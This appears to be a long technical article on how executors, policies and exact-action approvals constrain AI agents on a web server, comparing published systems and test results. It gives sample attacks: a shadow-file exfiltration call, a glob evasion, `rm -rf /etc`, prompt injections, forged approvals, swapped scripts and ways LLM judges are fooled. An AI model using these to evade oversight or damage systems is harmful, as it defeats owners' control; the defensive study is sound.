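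A reduction that removes content is therefore safe only if the executor runs the reduced form. Rundgren and colleagues let data travel in its original form while programs compute digests on the canonical one, which is reasonable for JCS because both forms decode to the same data. Faramesh needs the executor to run the canonical form, but Fatmi is not clear about whether it does. He writes in one passage that the system forwards the canonical action for execution, and in another that the deciding component does not carry payloads. In the second case, the tool gets its request by another route and would have to build the canonical form itself and run that.

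The W3C, which sets standards for the web, dealt with the same problem when it drafted rules for signing XML documents in 2000. Its rule, under the heading "'See' What is Signed", is that software relying on a signature should act on the transformed data that the signature covers, not on the original. Following this rule in the hosting example would leave the limit unchanged, as the owner approved, even if the agent wanted something else.

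Fatmi also wants requests with the same meaning to share a canonical form. In a second example, the English sentence "Deploy the payments service to production" and two JSON requests, one using the verb `deploy` and the other `release`, all become one record. But some software teams use "deploy" for installing a new version on the servers and "release" for making it available to customers, and would not want one approval to cover both. Interpreting an English sentence also brings back the guesswork that typed operations were meant to remove. An executor can avoid both problems by rejecting the sentence and the unfamiliar verb, and making the model process resend the request in the required form.

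### Types in name only

A request can look typed and still be a shell command. For example, an operation called `run_command` with one text argument has a name and a declared type, but these give the checker almost no information about what the command will do.

*From Craft to Kernel* (Wen, Chen and colleagues, 2026) proposes a typed instruction set for agents, but its code example has this weakness. The example starts with a call to a tool named `exec`, whose only argument is a line of shell text that reads the host's password file, `/etc/shadow`, and posts it to an attacker's website. The system turns the call into a record with typed labels and blocks it because it combines high confidentiality with low trustworthiness. However, some program has to read the shell text to know that the file is confidential, and it has to handle the same quoting, variables and wrappers as any other checker.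 An attacker could write `/etc/sh*dow`, which the shell would expand to the same file name.

The problem is harder to see in an operation such as `write_file`. Its path can be absolute and its digest exact, but if the host runs that file as a script every night, the operation lets the model process run any program a few hours later. `replace_file` has the same problem when the file is `shop.conf`, since nginx applies whatever directives the new text contains.

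*Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) separates content of this kind, called effect-bearing payloads, from opaque data. An effect-bearing payload looks like data but changes behaviour when something uses it. Examples include scripts, patches (lists of changes to a program's code), database commands, configuration files and the lists of packages that a project installs. Opaque data is text that the receiving system stores or displays without interpreting it, such as an error message quoted in a bug report.

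The same text can belong to either class, depending on where it goes. For example, `rm -rf /etc` is harmless in a comment but can delete the host's configuration files if it is in a script. A comment can also become effect-bearing if somebody later installs a bot that runs commands found in comments. Santos-Grueiro therefore counts a field as harmless only if the program that connects the agent to the tool can show that the tool will not interpret it. The system treats copied text as untrusted again if another agent later reads it.

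For an effect-bearing payload, the declared type "text" is far too loose. Santos-Grueiro's system authorises one exact effect and records what determines it:

| Payload | What the authorisation fixes |
|---|---|
| File | Path, exact bytes, permissions and the state of the target beforehand |
| Patch | Starting version of the project, and the old and new contents of each file, including links and renames |
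| Database command | Parsed command, its parameters, the database's structure, the role that runs it and what it may write |
| Shell command | Argument list built by trusted code, environment variables, working directory and sandbox limits |

The last row shows that even a shell command can become fairly exact if trusted code builds it and the sandbox limits what it can reach. An exactly specified effect can still be a bad one, and Santos-Grueiro leaves separate validators to judge whether it is.

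### Choosing the list of operations

Sometimes a designer can avoid the payload altogether. An operation `set_upload_limit` could take a site name and a whole number of megabytes and let the executor write the configuration line itself, so none of the model's text reaches the file. But the operation is nearly useless for anything else. If customers later complain that uploads time out, the agent needs a different operation, which may not exist.

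The strictest choice is to leave a dangerous operation out, as Agora does. Agora is a system in which an AI can start and monitor other AI workers. Quarry Systems' *The privilege boundary* lists the nine tools that the AI in charge can use while running, for tasks such as starting a job, cancelling it or checking its progress. No tool lets it register a new capability or change what a worker may do, because an attacker could use such a tool through prompt injection to give a worker new powers. Whenever developers change the software, an automated test compares the tools with the approved list, and the build fails if there is a tenth.

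Agora's AI cannot give itself a new capability, even when the job clearly needs one. A person has to define it first, and the AI can then use it by name. Adding narrow operations on demand this way keeps the decision with people, but work stops until somebody responds. In an executor, each new operation also adds code that runs with privilege. After a few hundred additions, the program may no longer meet Anderson's requirement that people can analyse and test all of it.

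A short list of tools can still give an agent broad power. Agora's tool for starting a job launches workers whose powers depend on the capabilities people registered earlier, which can include patterns of permitted shell commands. If somebody registers a capability that permits every shell command, Agora's nine tools are about as powerful as a shell.

Restricting the arguments of existing programs takes less work than writing new operations, because the programs are already there. Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, can do this with a line in a rules file for commands that it runs outside its sandbox. OpenAI's *Rules* explains that each rule specifies the words a command must begin with and whether Codex should run it, ask the user or refuse. *Running Codex safely* includes a rule from OpenAI's own configuration for `gh pr view` and `gh pr list`, which display proposed code changes on GitHub.

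Codex compares lists of separate arguments instead of raw text. It splits a script into individual commands only if the script consists of plain words joined by simple operators such as `&&`. If the script contains a variable, a wildcard, a redirection to a file or a loop, Codex treats the whole script as one command. The upload command contains `$LIMIT`, so Codex would not split it, and a rule allowing `systemctl restart nginx` would have no effect on it.

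That rule also specifies only the beginning of the command, so it permits `systemctl restart nginx postgresql`, which restarts a database as well. `restart_service` accepts only one name. Other programs have options that do much more. Anthropic notes that git's `-c` option can make git run a program of the caller's choice. Whoever writes such rules needs to know every option of every permitted program, and to check again when a new version comes out.

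Restrictions also conflict with how models tend to work. The developer Dylan Hurd wrote in a February 2026 change note in *Agent IDE*, a modified copy of the Codex code, that GPT-5.3-Codex "really likes to write complicated shell scripts". The model also proposed rules that would not have approved the scripts it had just written. A person then has to review the script, or the model has to find a simpler way to do the job.

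Santos-Grueiro's test on 400 coding tasks gives some idea of how often these restrictions stop an agent from finishing its work. The system completed 231 tasks safely and let no unauthorised action through. In 73 tasks it could not parse the model's output, and in 61 it could parse the request but had no authorisation for the effect. In the other 35, the agent's actions ran but did not solve the task. About a third of the tasks stopped before the agent could change anything. An agent with an ordinary shell would have failed some of these too, so the restrictions probably account for failures in less than a third of the tasks.

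### Agents that click

Declared types add little when an agent works through clicks and keystrokes. `click(x: 640, y: 412)` is a well-typed operation with two whole numbers and an obvious canonical form, but its effect depends on what is at that point on the screen when the click arrives. If a window moves, the same click can land on "Delete" instead of "Cancel" with no change to its digest. An agent that can send keystrokes to a terminal window can enter a shell command one letter at a time.

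The executor could require the name of a button instead of its position. Many applications already supply these names for screen readers. A request to press "Restart" in the window "Services" is easier to check than a pair of coordinates. But the application's developer chooses both the label and what the button does, and on a web page that developer may be the attacker.

Typed operations can still limit where the agent acts, such as which applications may receive clicks or which websites the browser may open. For finer control, the designer has to provide a separate operation such as `restart_service` and block the agent's mouse and keyboard input to any window that can do the same thing.

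## How does the executor decide what to allow?

A typed operation is easy to read, but the executor still has to decide whether to carry it out. UT Austin's *Authorization you build*, a set of lecture slides, breaks this decision into questions, using the example of a program that publishes students' grades. On the web server, the executor would check in this order:

1. Is the request well formed? It must name an operation on the list and supply every argument with the declared type. A `write_site_config` request with no text fails.
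2. Do the named objects exist? A request for the site `shpo` fails because the executor's table has no such site.
3. May this requester cause this effect? The model process may not change the payment site, however carefully it writes the request.
4. Does the effect need approval?
5. If it does, has the owner approved this exact action?

The policy refers to sites and services, so the executor has to identify them before it can apply a rule. Asking for approval last also spares the owner from reviewing requests that could never run. A small drawback of this order is that a hijacked model process can find out which sites exist if the executor returns "no such site" for one name and "not permitted" for another. The owner can prevent this by having the executor return the same answer in both cases.

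### A policy with three verdicts

A policy for the server could consist of three rules:

```
allow    restart_service     service is nginx
ask      write_site_config   site is shop
refuse   write_site_config   site is payments
```

"Allow" means the executor acts at once, "ask" means it waits for the owner, and "refuse" means it only reports the refusal to the model process. If several rules match a request, the strictest applies. If none matches, the executor refuses.

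| Request | Verdict | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| `restart_service`, nginx | Allow | The first rule matches |
| `write_site_config`, shop | Ask | The second rule matches |
| `write_site_config`, payments | Refuse | The third rule matches |
| `restart_service`, postgresql | Refuse | No rule matches |
| Any request, while the policy file is unreadable | Refuse | The executor cannot complete the check |

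The database in the fourth row exists, and no rule forbids restarting it. The request fails only because no rule allows it.

The upload task combines the first two rows in one manifest. The executor should hold both operations until the owner approves, since restarting nginx before the file changes would interrupt visitors with no benefit. Faramesh gives each action a verdict of PERMIT, DEFER or DENY and lets it run only if the verdict is PERMIT, so a deferred action has no more effect on the host than a denied one.

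UT Austin suggests choosing between the verdicts by how serious an effect is and whether anyone can undo it. Reading files and running tests can be automatic, while sending an email or deploying software needs a person's approval, and deleting data may need two people. By that standard the nginx restart is borderline because it briefly interrupts every site on the server, so the owner of a busy site might change that rule to "ask".

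### When a rule is missing or broken

If the owner leaves a stray character in the policy and the executor can't parse the file, the executor should refuse everything, including the restart it allowed a minute earlier. Jing included 32 such faults in the full set of test cases, among them a missing or corrupted policy and a log the system could not write to.

OASIS's *xacml v4.0 csd01*, a draft of a general standard for access policies, has four possible decisions: Permit, Deny, NotApplicable (no rule covers the request) and Indeterminate (the check failed). An earlier OASIS draft did not define how the basic enforcement program should respond to the last two, but it also described a "deny-biased" version that refuses a request unless the decision is Permit. An executor should be deny-biased, but it can still log the four decisions separately, so that an owner who finds "indeterminate" in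 the log knows to repair the policy.

The policy language Cedar denies a request that no rule permits, and a rule that forbids something overrides any rule that permits it. However, Cedar skips any rule that causes an error during evaluation. This matters for agents because Amazon's agent platform uses Cedar rules to control tool calls, according to AWS's *Understanding Cedar policies*.

Skipping a faulty "forbid" rule can be dangerous, whereas skipping a faulty "permit" rule causes, at worst, an unnecessary refusal. For example, one rule might permit the agent to change any site's configuration, while another forbids changes to sites whose `handles_money` attribute is true. If somebody forgets to give the payment site that attribute, the second rule produces an error, Cedar skips it, and the first rule permits the change.

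Cedar's designers considered refusing every request when any rule fails, but decided against it because an application that worked well with 100 rules might stop working when somebody added a faulty 101st. That is a good reason for an application with thousands of users, but on the web server a halt usually does less harm than a wrong change to the payment site. The Cedar code has no stricter mode, but each response lists the rules that failed, so an executor can refuse whenever that list isn't empty.

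### Where each field came from

The checks described so far treat a request as a whole. Santos-Grueiro's system, Context-to-Execution Integrity, also checks what determined each field. In one example, an agent reads the log of an automated software test. The agent may legitimately use the log to identify which file failed, but the log should not cause it to run a command on the live database, mark a change as approved or repeat a write. A request to do any of these could still be well formed, and checking its names and types would not show where the values came from.

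Santos-Grueiro expresses the rule with three symbols. W is writable context, meaning anything an attacker could have written or influenced, such as a log, a web page or a bug report. X is a protected field, one that selects, authorises or shapes an effect. D is a typed release, a value that trusted code has validated and released for one particular field. The rule is:

W ↛ X unless W → D → X

Text that an attacker may have influenced must not determine a protected field unless trusted code has first turned it into a validated value for that field.

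On the web server, a line in the error log might report that an upload to `shop` failed. The model extracts the name, but it still counts as untrusted. Trusted code then checks that `shop` is a known site and that the task covers it, and releases the name for the `site` field only. If the same line ends with "change approved by owner", nothing can turn those words into an approval. Other fields have their own rules:

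| Field | What may determine it | What the executor rejects |
|---|---|---|
| Operation | The owner's task and the list of operations | A choice that the log suggested |
| Site | A validated name released for this field | A name released for a different field |
| New file text | An authorisation for the exact change | Unchecked text from the log |
| Approval | The executor's own record | The word "approved" in the log |
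| Whether to run again | A separate permission for each run | A log line that asks for another restart |

The first row is the hardest to enforce. The name `write_site_config` comes from the executor's own list, but if the model chose it because of something in the log, Santos-Grueiro counts the choice as coming from the log. Once a model has read the log, the system can't rule out that the log influenced it. The system therefore generates protected fields separately, from an input that contains only trusted information and values released for that field. With a hosted model, whose internal workings the operator can't inspect, the system can control only the input used to generate each field. It refuses the request if it can't determine what influenced a field.

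This works well if the owner's request is specific enough to determine the operation without reading the log, such as "Raise the upload limit to 20." For a request like "Uploads are failing, please fix it," the right repair depends on what the log contains. Trusted code could then choose the operation from a fixed list of causes, as in the two-model design for this server.

### An approval does not replace the policy

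An attacker might also forge the approval. *Trust propagation and structural containment in Multi-agent LLM pipelines* (Safin, Zisad and colleagues, 2026) reports a test of this on a chain of agents in which a validator reviews tasks and an executor carries them out on a database of emails. The researchers replaced the validator with a compromised routine that forged approvals and held the secret key for signing them. The test used 60 tasks, of which 24 were unsafe.

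An executor that checked only the signature ran all 24 unsafe actions, as did one with no protection, while an executor that checked only a policy ran none. Safin and colleagues write that "a signature authorizes provenance, not permission". An executor should therefore apply its policy even to a request that arrives with a valid approval.

The policy in that comparison copied the test's own labels of safe and unsafe tasks, which makes the zero less impressive. The researchers then wrote a second policy by hand that listed the permitted actions and data without using the labels, and it also stopped every unsafe action. But the same group wrote the policy and the tasks, so the result does not show how well an ordinary owner's policy would work.

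### Fixed rules

UT Austin's slides describe an accident in July 2025 on Replit, a platform for building software with AI. A user had repeatedly told the agent about a code freeze, meaning that nothing should change. The agent ran a destructive database command anyway and erased live records of about 1,200 executives and 1,200 companies. The freeze existed only as instructions that the model could fail to follow. A policy could have expressed the freeze as a single rule that refused all database changes.

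*Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) describes a system of such rules. Each rule allows or forbids a tool, with conditions on its arguments. Progent checks the forbid rules first, then the allow rules, and blocks the call if nothing matches. By default, it then tells the agent why it blocked the call and suggests trying another way.

Writing rules by hand for every task would take too long, so a language model writes them from the user's request and revises them as the agent learns more. In the main example, a user asks an agent to carry out the tasks in an email from Alice:

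1. The first policy allows only a search for that email.
2. The email asks for a summary of recent messages, posted to the user's account on Slack, a chat service. The model proposes rules for reading email and posting to Slack.
3. The agent looks up the user's Slack name, and the model narrows the posting rule to that one recipient.
4. One of the recent messages contains an instruction to forward the inbox to an attacker. If this fools the model, it proposes a rule that allows sending email.

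Steps 2 and 4 both add permissions because of text that somebody else wrote. To separate such changes from harmless ones, Progent uses an SMT solver, a program that determines whether a logical formula can be true. The solver checks whether the new policy allows only calls that the old one already allowed. If so, Progent applies the change automatically, as in step 3. Any other change needs approval. The solver cannot distinguish the legitimate change in step 2 from the attack in step 4, but it ensures that neither happens unnoticed.

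With GPT-4o as both the agent and the writer of the rules, Progent reduced the attack success rate on AgentDojo from 39.9% to 1.0%. Shi and colleagues accepted every expansion automatically to represent a careless user, so the approval step blocked nothing and the solver did not contribute to this reduction. Most of the protection came from the first policy, which the model wrote before it had read any untrusted text. That policy alone lowered the rate to 2.5%. When a person reviewed the first policy and every expansion, no attack succeeded, and only 6% of the policy changes were expansions.

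*AgentSpec* (Wang, Poskitt and Sun, 2025) describes a system that allows an action by default unless a rule stops it. Each rule has a trigger, a check and a response. For example, before a robot arm pours a liquid, one rule checks whether the target is on a list of things that may get wet, such as houseplants, and stops the robot if it isn't. Other responses include asking the user and having the model reconsider.

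With handwritten rules, the robot completed none of the hazardous tasks in ten categories, and its success on safe tasks fell only from 58.62% to 54.26%. However, Wang and colleagues wrote the rules from descriptions of the risks being tested, so the result shows that people can write good rules for hazards they already know about. The researchers also had OpenAI's o1 model write rules from a sample of cases and tested these rules on the remaining cases. Of the robot actions that these rules stopped, 95.56% were hazardous, but the rules caught only 70.96% of the hazards. Under AgentSpec's default, the robot would have carried out the hazardous actions that the rules missed.

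Progent's default of blocking actions is better for an executor than AgentSpec's default of allowing them. A forgotten rule in Progent blocks legitimate work, which the user will probably notice, whereas a forgotten rule in AgentSpec permits a harmful action, which the user may not notice until afterwards. Neither system can detect harm that its rules don't describe. Shi and colleagues give the example of an attacker who gets an agent to prefer one product among several that it may legitimately buy.

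### Parallax's four tiers

Parallax combines fixed rules with methods that can handle cases the rules don't cover. An action passes through up to four tiers, and Fokou puts the most predictable tier first.

Tier 0 is a policy file with three sections, which Parallax reads in order. The first denies some actions, such as reading the folder that holds a user's login keys. The second sends others to a later tier, for example all shell commands to Tier 1. The third allows safe actions, such as reading files in the agent's workspace. An action that matches no rule goes to Tier 1, whereas on the web server a missing rule leads directly to refusal.

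Tier 1 runs two checks at the same time. One compares the action with 37 known dangerous patterns, such as a command that downloads a program and runs it immediately. The other uses a classifier, a small model that estimates whether a text contains prompt injection. Tier 1 blocks the action if it matches a pattern or if the classifier flags it with a confidence of at least 0.85. A less confident flag sends the action to Tier 2. If neither check flags the action, it runs.

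In Tier 2, a separate language model judges the action. This judge receives the action's type and content, but not the conversation, user profile or task description. It must also repeat a secret string in its answer. If instructions hidden in the content take over the judge, it may leave the string out, and Parallax then blocks the action. This check would not catch an injection that changed only the verdict.

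Tier 3 asks a person, and refuses if nobody answers within five minutes.

The later tiers can consider the content of an action in ways that a list of paths cannot, but they also make mistakes. When Fokou tried 50 legitimate actions with the classifier switched on for every type of action, Parallax blocked 18. The classifier caused 14 of the refusals, all at a confidence of 1.00. It had been trained on examples of prompt injection in text and misclassified ordinary file contents and emails as attacks. The judge caused the other four, which are hard for an owner to correct because, as Fokou notes, they might not recur in another run.

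By default, Parallax avoids the 14 errors by sending seven types of action, including writing and deleting files, straight to the judge instead of the classifier. However, the judge allowed an `env` command because the command is read-only, even though it prints the environment variables, which often include passwords. The judge isn't shown the task, which makes it harder to manipulate but also prevents it from checking whether the user wanted the action.

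The judge can make only 100 decisions a day by default, so that an attacker can't run up unlimited costs. Fokou intends Tiers 0 and 1 to keep the system safe once that limit is reached. But file writes skip the classifier by default, so only the fixed rules and patterns would check their contents. An executor built this way should refuse file writes until the next day.

Parallax also has an exception to its rule of failing closed. It blocks an action if the classifier crashes while checking it, but if nobody has installed the classifier, Parallax starts anyway, logs one warning and relies on the patterns. An owner who misses that warning will have less protection than the design is meant to provide.

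Microsoft combines the methods differently in its Agent Control Specification, which passes the results of classifiers and model-based judges to a policy engine as additional inputs. On the web server, the owner could write a rule that changes "allow" to "ask" when a classifier flags something suspicious. If classifier results can never make a verdict more lenient, a false alarm means the owner has to answer an unnecessary question, and a missed attack leaves the verdict unchanged.

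### Who writes the policy, and who can change it

Several parties may want to shape the policy. The company that runs an agent may want rules about customer data, the agent's developer may want to restrict certain tools, and the user may want to protect personal files. Progent lets each of them write fixed rules and ranks them by authority. It applies the rules a model writes for a task only where the fixed rules do not cover an action, so the model cannot permit what the company has forbidden.

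*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) raises two objections to Progent. Progent's guarantees depend on people writing correct and complete policies, which is error-prone, and malicious text in a tool result may lead to a policy update that loosens the limits. The solver resolves the second objection if whoever reviews the expansions rejects the bad ones. The first objection remains because the solver only compares the new policy with the old one, without checking whether the old one was right.

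Even if the model process cannot write to the executor's policy file, a hijacked process might request that the executor replace the file, since the executor can write to the host. Parallax prevents this with checks compiled into its program, which run before Tier 0 and block all access to the main configuration file and the log. No setting can switch them off. Jing stores digests of the policy and its enforcement program where the agent cannot write, so that anyone who compares them later can detect a change. Text that the agent reads can't alter the policy either. In Santos-Grueiro's system, a message announcing an emergency exception has no effect unless trusted code confirms it.

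None of this helps if the policy was wrong from the start. Fokou's first version had no rules against reading `/etc/passwd`, which lists the computer's user accounts, or `.env` files, which often contain passwords. Fokou found these gaps by testing and obtained the 98.9% block rate only after adding rules for them and 17 new patterns to Tier 1. New attacks would probably expose other gaps.

It is easy to overlook that a policy is too strict. One of the four defects Jing found in the governance layer made it stricter than intended. The defect did not show up in the overall scores, because a system that blocks too much does well on attacks. Jing's test cases include ordinary tasks, and each case lists the correct verdict in advance. The owner of a web server could keep a similar list and run it after every policy change. Otherwise, the owner finds out that the policy is too strict when the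 executor refuses legitimate work, and may respond by allowing `write_site_config` for every site. A hijacked model process could then rewrite the payment site without anyone's approval.

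## How is an approval tied to one exact action?

When the policy sends a change to the owner, the answer may take minutes or hours, and somebody can alter the change while it waits. Suppose the agent writes `cleanup.sh`, a script that deletes old log files from the web server. The owner reads the script and approves it, and the executor records the approval under the file's name. A hijacked model process that can still write to the file then replaces its contents with a command that deletes the shop's database. When the process requests to run `cleanup.sh`, the approval still counts because it is tied only to the file name.

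The check-to-use gap is the time between checking something and using it. Jing's first governance layer was vulnerable during this gap because it compared the request's digest with the approved one but did not check the script's contents. An attacker could get a script approved, replace it and run the replacement.

Agents also face the gap when no approval is involved, if they read a file or web page and act on it after it has changed. A survey, *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents* (2026), lists only two papers on this problem. One of them, *Mind the Gap* (Lilienthal and Hong, 2025), measures it with 66 tasks. Three defences combined (rewriting prompts, monitoring for changes and fusing tools) lowered the rate of such vulnerabilities only from 12% to 8%. An executor should do better with approved actions because it controls both the check and the use.

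Banks already deal with a version of this problem in online payments. European rules require the confirmation code to be linked to the amount and the payee, as Kodathala, Pollishetty and Cargill (2026) explain in *Approve What, Exactly?* If either changes, the code stops working. An agent's action has more parts than a payment, so the executor needs a longer record of what the owner approved.

### From manifest to action

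That record is the manifest, M. For the upload limit, it might contain:

```
operation 1       replace_file
  path            /etc/nginx/sites/shop.conf
  leads to        /etc/nginx/sites/shop.conf
  new text        SHA-256 digest of the proposed file
operation 2       restart_service
  service         nginx
requester         model process, session 318
host              web-1
environment       working directory /, standard variables only
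policy            version 12
expected state    SHA-256 digest of the current shop.conf
unique number     128 random bits
expires           14:15
```

The executor handles it in six steps:

1. It copies the proposed text into storage that the model process cannot write to, follows any links in the path, reads the current file and fills in M.
2. It puts M into canonical form and computes d = SHA-256(M).
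3. The owner reviews the change and authorises d.
4. Before acting, the executor computes the digests again from the stored text and manifest. It refuses if the result differs from the d that the owner authorised, if the approval has expired, if the policy version has changed or if `shop.conf` is no longer in the expected state.
5. It marks the approval as spent, in one indivisible step.
6. It writes the stored text to `shop.conf` and restarts nginx.

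Suppose the new text contains the line `client_max_body_size 20m;`, and after the owner approves, an attacker changes the `m` to a `g`. This raises the upload limit from 20 megabytes to 20 gigabytes, so a few uploads could fill the disk. But it also changes the text's digest, which changes a line of M and therefore d, so the executor refuses at step 4.

The executor would also refuse a change that seems safer than the approved one. In *ZeroGate*, a design for checking approved actions just before release, Wang (2026) describes an agent that may refund up to 60 units and holds an approval for 40. The agent cannot use that approval to refund 30, because the approval covers one action and doesn't set a limit.

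Each field in the manifest prevents a different misuse:

| Field | What could happen without it |
|---|---|
| Operation and arguments | An approval to restart nginx also permits a change to a file |
| Digest of the new text | An attacker swaps the text after the owner reads it |
| Resolved target | Somebody redirects a link, and the text lands in the payment site's file |
| Requester | Another agent uses the approval |
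| Host | An approval for the test server works on the live one |
| Environment | A changed variable makes an approved command run a different program |
| Policy version | A change goes ahead after the owner has tightened the rules against it |
| Expected state | The new text overwrites an edit the owner made in the meantime |
| Unique number | One approval covers every later request for the same action |
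| Expiry time | A forgotten approval takes effect months later |

The executor must also keep the fields separate when it computes the digest. If it joined the values together, session 31 with policy version 812 would produce the same text as session 318 with version 12. Kodathala and colleagues avoid this by hashing a JSON object in which every value has a name.

More detail in the manifest means more refusals. If the expected state included the error log, which changes with every failed upload, almost every approval would be invalid by step 4. The expected state should include only what the owner's decision depends on. UT Austin's slides give the example of a course quiz that an agent may publish only if it is still unpublished and no student has attempted it. If either condition has changed, the old approval no longer applies and the agent has to prepare a new request.

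### Hash the bytes that will run

The executor writes the stored text at step 6 instead of reading the file again, because the file could have changed since it was checked. A simpler executor might open `cleanup.sh`, compute its digest, find that it matches and tell the shell to run `cleanup.sh`. The shell then opens the file again by name, so an attacker who replaces it between the two openings can make the shell run a file that the executor did not check.

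Keeping the file open doesn't fully solve this, because a program with write access can still change the file. The executor needs a private copy that it reads once, hashes and runs. Wang describes the same error in network requests, where a program hashes one message but sends another, so the matching digest has no bearing on what the receiving service does.

A private copy covers only its own bytes. If the approved script runs `./helper.sh` or downloads another program, the owner's approval doesn't cover the contents of either. The manifest then needs a digest for each extra file, or the sandbox has to stop the script from reaching those files.

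Sometimes the executor cannot store exactly what will run, because somebody else's software builds the final request. When an agent pays through a website, for example, the page may show one recipient and then rewrite a hidden field as the browser submits the form. *The Verifiable Action Card* (2026) describes a system that records the recipient and amount at approval. As the request leaves the browser, the system compares both with the record and aborts if either differs. The check works however the page changed those two values, but it would presumably miss a change to anything else, such as a delivery address.

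On the web server, an administrator could also save an edit to `shop.conf` in the short gap between step 4, when the executor checks the current file, and step 6, when the executor replaces it. The executor can make this less likely by locking the file, if other programs respect the lock.

### One approval, one run

Suppose a server's owner has set nginx restarts to "ask", and approves one on Monday and another on Thursday. Without a unique number and an expiry time, the two manifests could be identical and have the same digest. The executor would then have to either accept that digest twice, which would let anyone replay Monday's approval, or refuse Thursday's restart. With different numbers, each restart has its own digest and needs its own approval.

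The executor also uses the number to recognise a retry. If the connection drops before the model process receives the result of Monday's restart, the model process can send the request again with the same number. The executor finds that it has already acted on that request and returns the earlier result.

Faramesh identifies duplicates by the digest of the canonical action. Fatmi sent it a million copies of one request through 64 parallel workers, and the action never ran twice. However, the canonical action in Fatmi's worked example has no unique number. If restart requests also lacked one, Faramesh would treat a restart on Thursday as a duplicate of an identical one on Monday and not run it.

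Spending must be indivisible because two copies of a request can arrive at almost the same moment. If the executor first looks up the approval and then marks it as spent, both copies may find it unspent and both may run. A single database command avoids this:

```
UPDATE approvals SET status = 'spent'
WHERE digest = d AND status = 'approved'
```

The database applies the command for one copy at a time. The first copy changes a row, and the executor proceeds. For the second, there is no row left to change, so the executor does not act again. ZeroGate uses SQLite, a small database that runs inside another program. In one transaction, ZeroGate marks the number as used, deducts from any quota and records the decision, so either all three changes take effect or none does.

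This protection works only within a single database. Wang points out that two regions with separate databases could each accept a copy of the same approval. Naming the host in the manifest prevents this if each server checks that the name is its own.

Restoring an old copy of the records can also make a spent approval usable again. Kodathala and colleagues audited ten agent runtimes, the software that runs an agent's loop of model calls and actions. In five of them, an approved action ran a second time after the researchers rolled the run back to an earlier state, because the approval had no unique number or expiry time. An executor should therefore keep its records where the model process cannot restore them. The owner could still revive old approvals by restoring the whole server from a backup, which is a good reason for a short expiry time, such as the 15 minutes UT Austin uses.

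### What a crash leaves behind

If the power fails after the executor marks the approval as used but before it writes the file, the shop keeps its old limit and the approval can't be used again. The reverse order can do more damage, because if the executor acted first and crashed before marking the approval as used, the approval would still work. Writing the same configuration file twice is harmless, but sending a refund twice costs the company money.

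A spent approval therefore shows only that the executor had permission to act. Wang keeps this record separate from evidence of the effect, because the record can survive a crash even if nothing happened outside the database. When the executor starts again, it should look for spent approvals that have no recorded result and inspect the host:

- If `shop.conf` has the old digest, the change did not happen, and the agent needs a new approval to try again.
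- If the file has the new digest but nginx has been running since before the approval, only the restart is missing.
- If the file has some other digest, a person should look at it.

An outside service is harder to inspect. After a timeout, the executor cannot determine from its own database whether a payment went through. Santos-Grueiro therefore does not promise in general that an outside effect happens exactly once. That requires the receiving service to help, for example by recognising and ignoring repeated requests.

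### What Jing's tests found

Jing's full set of 313 test cases includes 31 attacks that take place after approval. Some alter the script or the request, while others forge an approval's identifier, replay a used approval or apply an approval to a different operation. Jing ran these against two versions of the governance layer that differed only in whether the executor checked the file's bytes before running it. The check raised the number of blocked attacks from 19 (61.3%) to 28 (90.3%). Adding the operating system's sandbox, which had helped a great deal against disguised commands, did not stop the remaining three.

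Making approvals single-use raised the share of replay attacks blocked from 77.8% to 100%. The 31 attacks tested include several other kinds, so this improvement probably comes from a handful of cases.

These percentages count the actions the layer would have permitted, without running every action. Jing also tried seven alteration attacks for real on a decoy file. Two deleted the file before the byte check was added, and none of the seven ran afterwards.

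One person designed both the attacks and the defence, and the numbers are small. An executor that checks for altered bytes should be expected to detect them, so the more useful finding is that developers can easily leave such a check out. Jing's design reviews missed both flaws. The replay flaw was especially hard to see because the layer's recorded decision looked normal, and Jing found it only by sending a used approval again. The audit by Kodathala and colleagues suggests that other developers make similar mistakes. Of the eight runtimes where they could test whether the approved action stayed fixed, three passed, one passed in part, and four let something change the action after approval. These results are for the runtimes' standard approval features, and a careful developer could add the missing checks.

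Jing's executor itself now records that an approval has been used, so a failure in a later clean-up step cannot leave the approval usable. The layer reads Jing's log to see whether an approval has been used, so a lost entry could make a used approval valid again. When two programs wrote to the log at once, it lost 9.66% of its entries, and with eight programs it lost 31.32%. Jing stopped the losses by locking the file and forcing each entry onto the disk, which made each write take about 4.5 times as long.

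### Leases and signed artefacts

Context-to-Execution Integrity and Faramesh both require proof of permission before a tool runs, but they create that proof at different times.

In Santos-Grueiro's system, a ledger holds a permission for one action, tied to the digest of that action's manifest. The tool needs a lease to run, and the ledger issues one only after the system has used up the permission. Santos-Grueiro tested the ledger with ten kinds of fault and 29 attempts to use up a permission. The ledger rejected 19 attempts and identified two as retries, and no action ran twice.

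Fatmi's system, Faramesh, creates a signed artefact when it permits an action. The artefact contains the action's digest, the policy version and a digest of the system's state, and it expires. The executor refuses to act without one. A signature is useful if the decision and the action take place on different machines, because the executor can verify it with a key without contacting the machine that made the decision. But a copy of a signed artefact is as valid as the original, so Faramesh still needs its ledger to prevent replays.

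Fatmi made 10,000 attempts to call a tool directly and another 10,000 to reuse an artefact for a different action, and none succeeded. These results are hard to reconcile with the "coverage" of 0.9993 that Fatmi reports for normal operation. Fatmi defines coverage as the share of attempts that did not result in an action running without a valid artefact. Taken literally, this means 0.07% of attempts did result in an action running without one. Fatmi attributes the shortfall to faults and malformed requests that the test program introduced deliberately, but an executor that fails closed should have refused those too.

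The design by Kodathala and colleagues can tie an approval to an action in two ways. Normally the executor stores the approved action and runs that stored version when the agent returns with the approval's identifier. If the agent also sends arguments and their digest differs from the approved one, nothing runs. Alternatively, it can issue a short-lived signed token that the receiving service accepts once. Across 27,108 scripted trials and 609 attacks based on AgentDojo, the design stopped substitutions and replays, whereas an approval with no link to the action allowed them every time. Kodathala and colleagues also used Tamarin, a program that searches a mathematical model of a protocol for attacks, to prove that each approval works once and only for its own action. The proof depends on three assumptions, including that the approver sees an accurate description of the action.

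### Draft formats for approval receipts

If an agent's owner approves a payment, the bank may want to check that approval with its own software. In 2026, several developers proposed formats that would allow this in Internet-Drafts, documents that anyone can submit to the Internet Engineering Task Force, which publishes many of the internet's technical standards. A draft lasts at most six months unless its author updates it and, according to its own notice, should be cited only as work in progress. The drafts described here are individual proposals, not standards.

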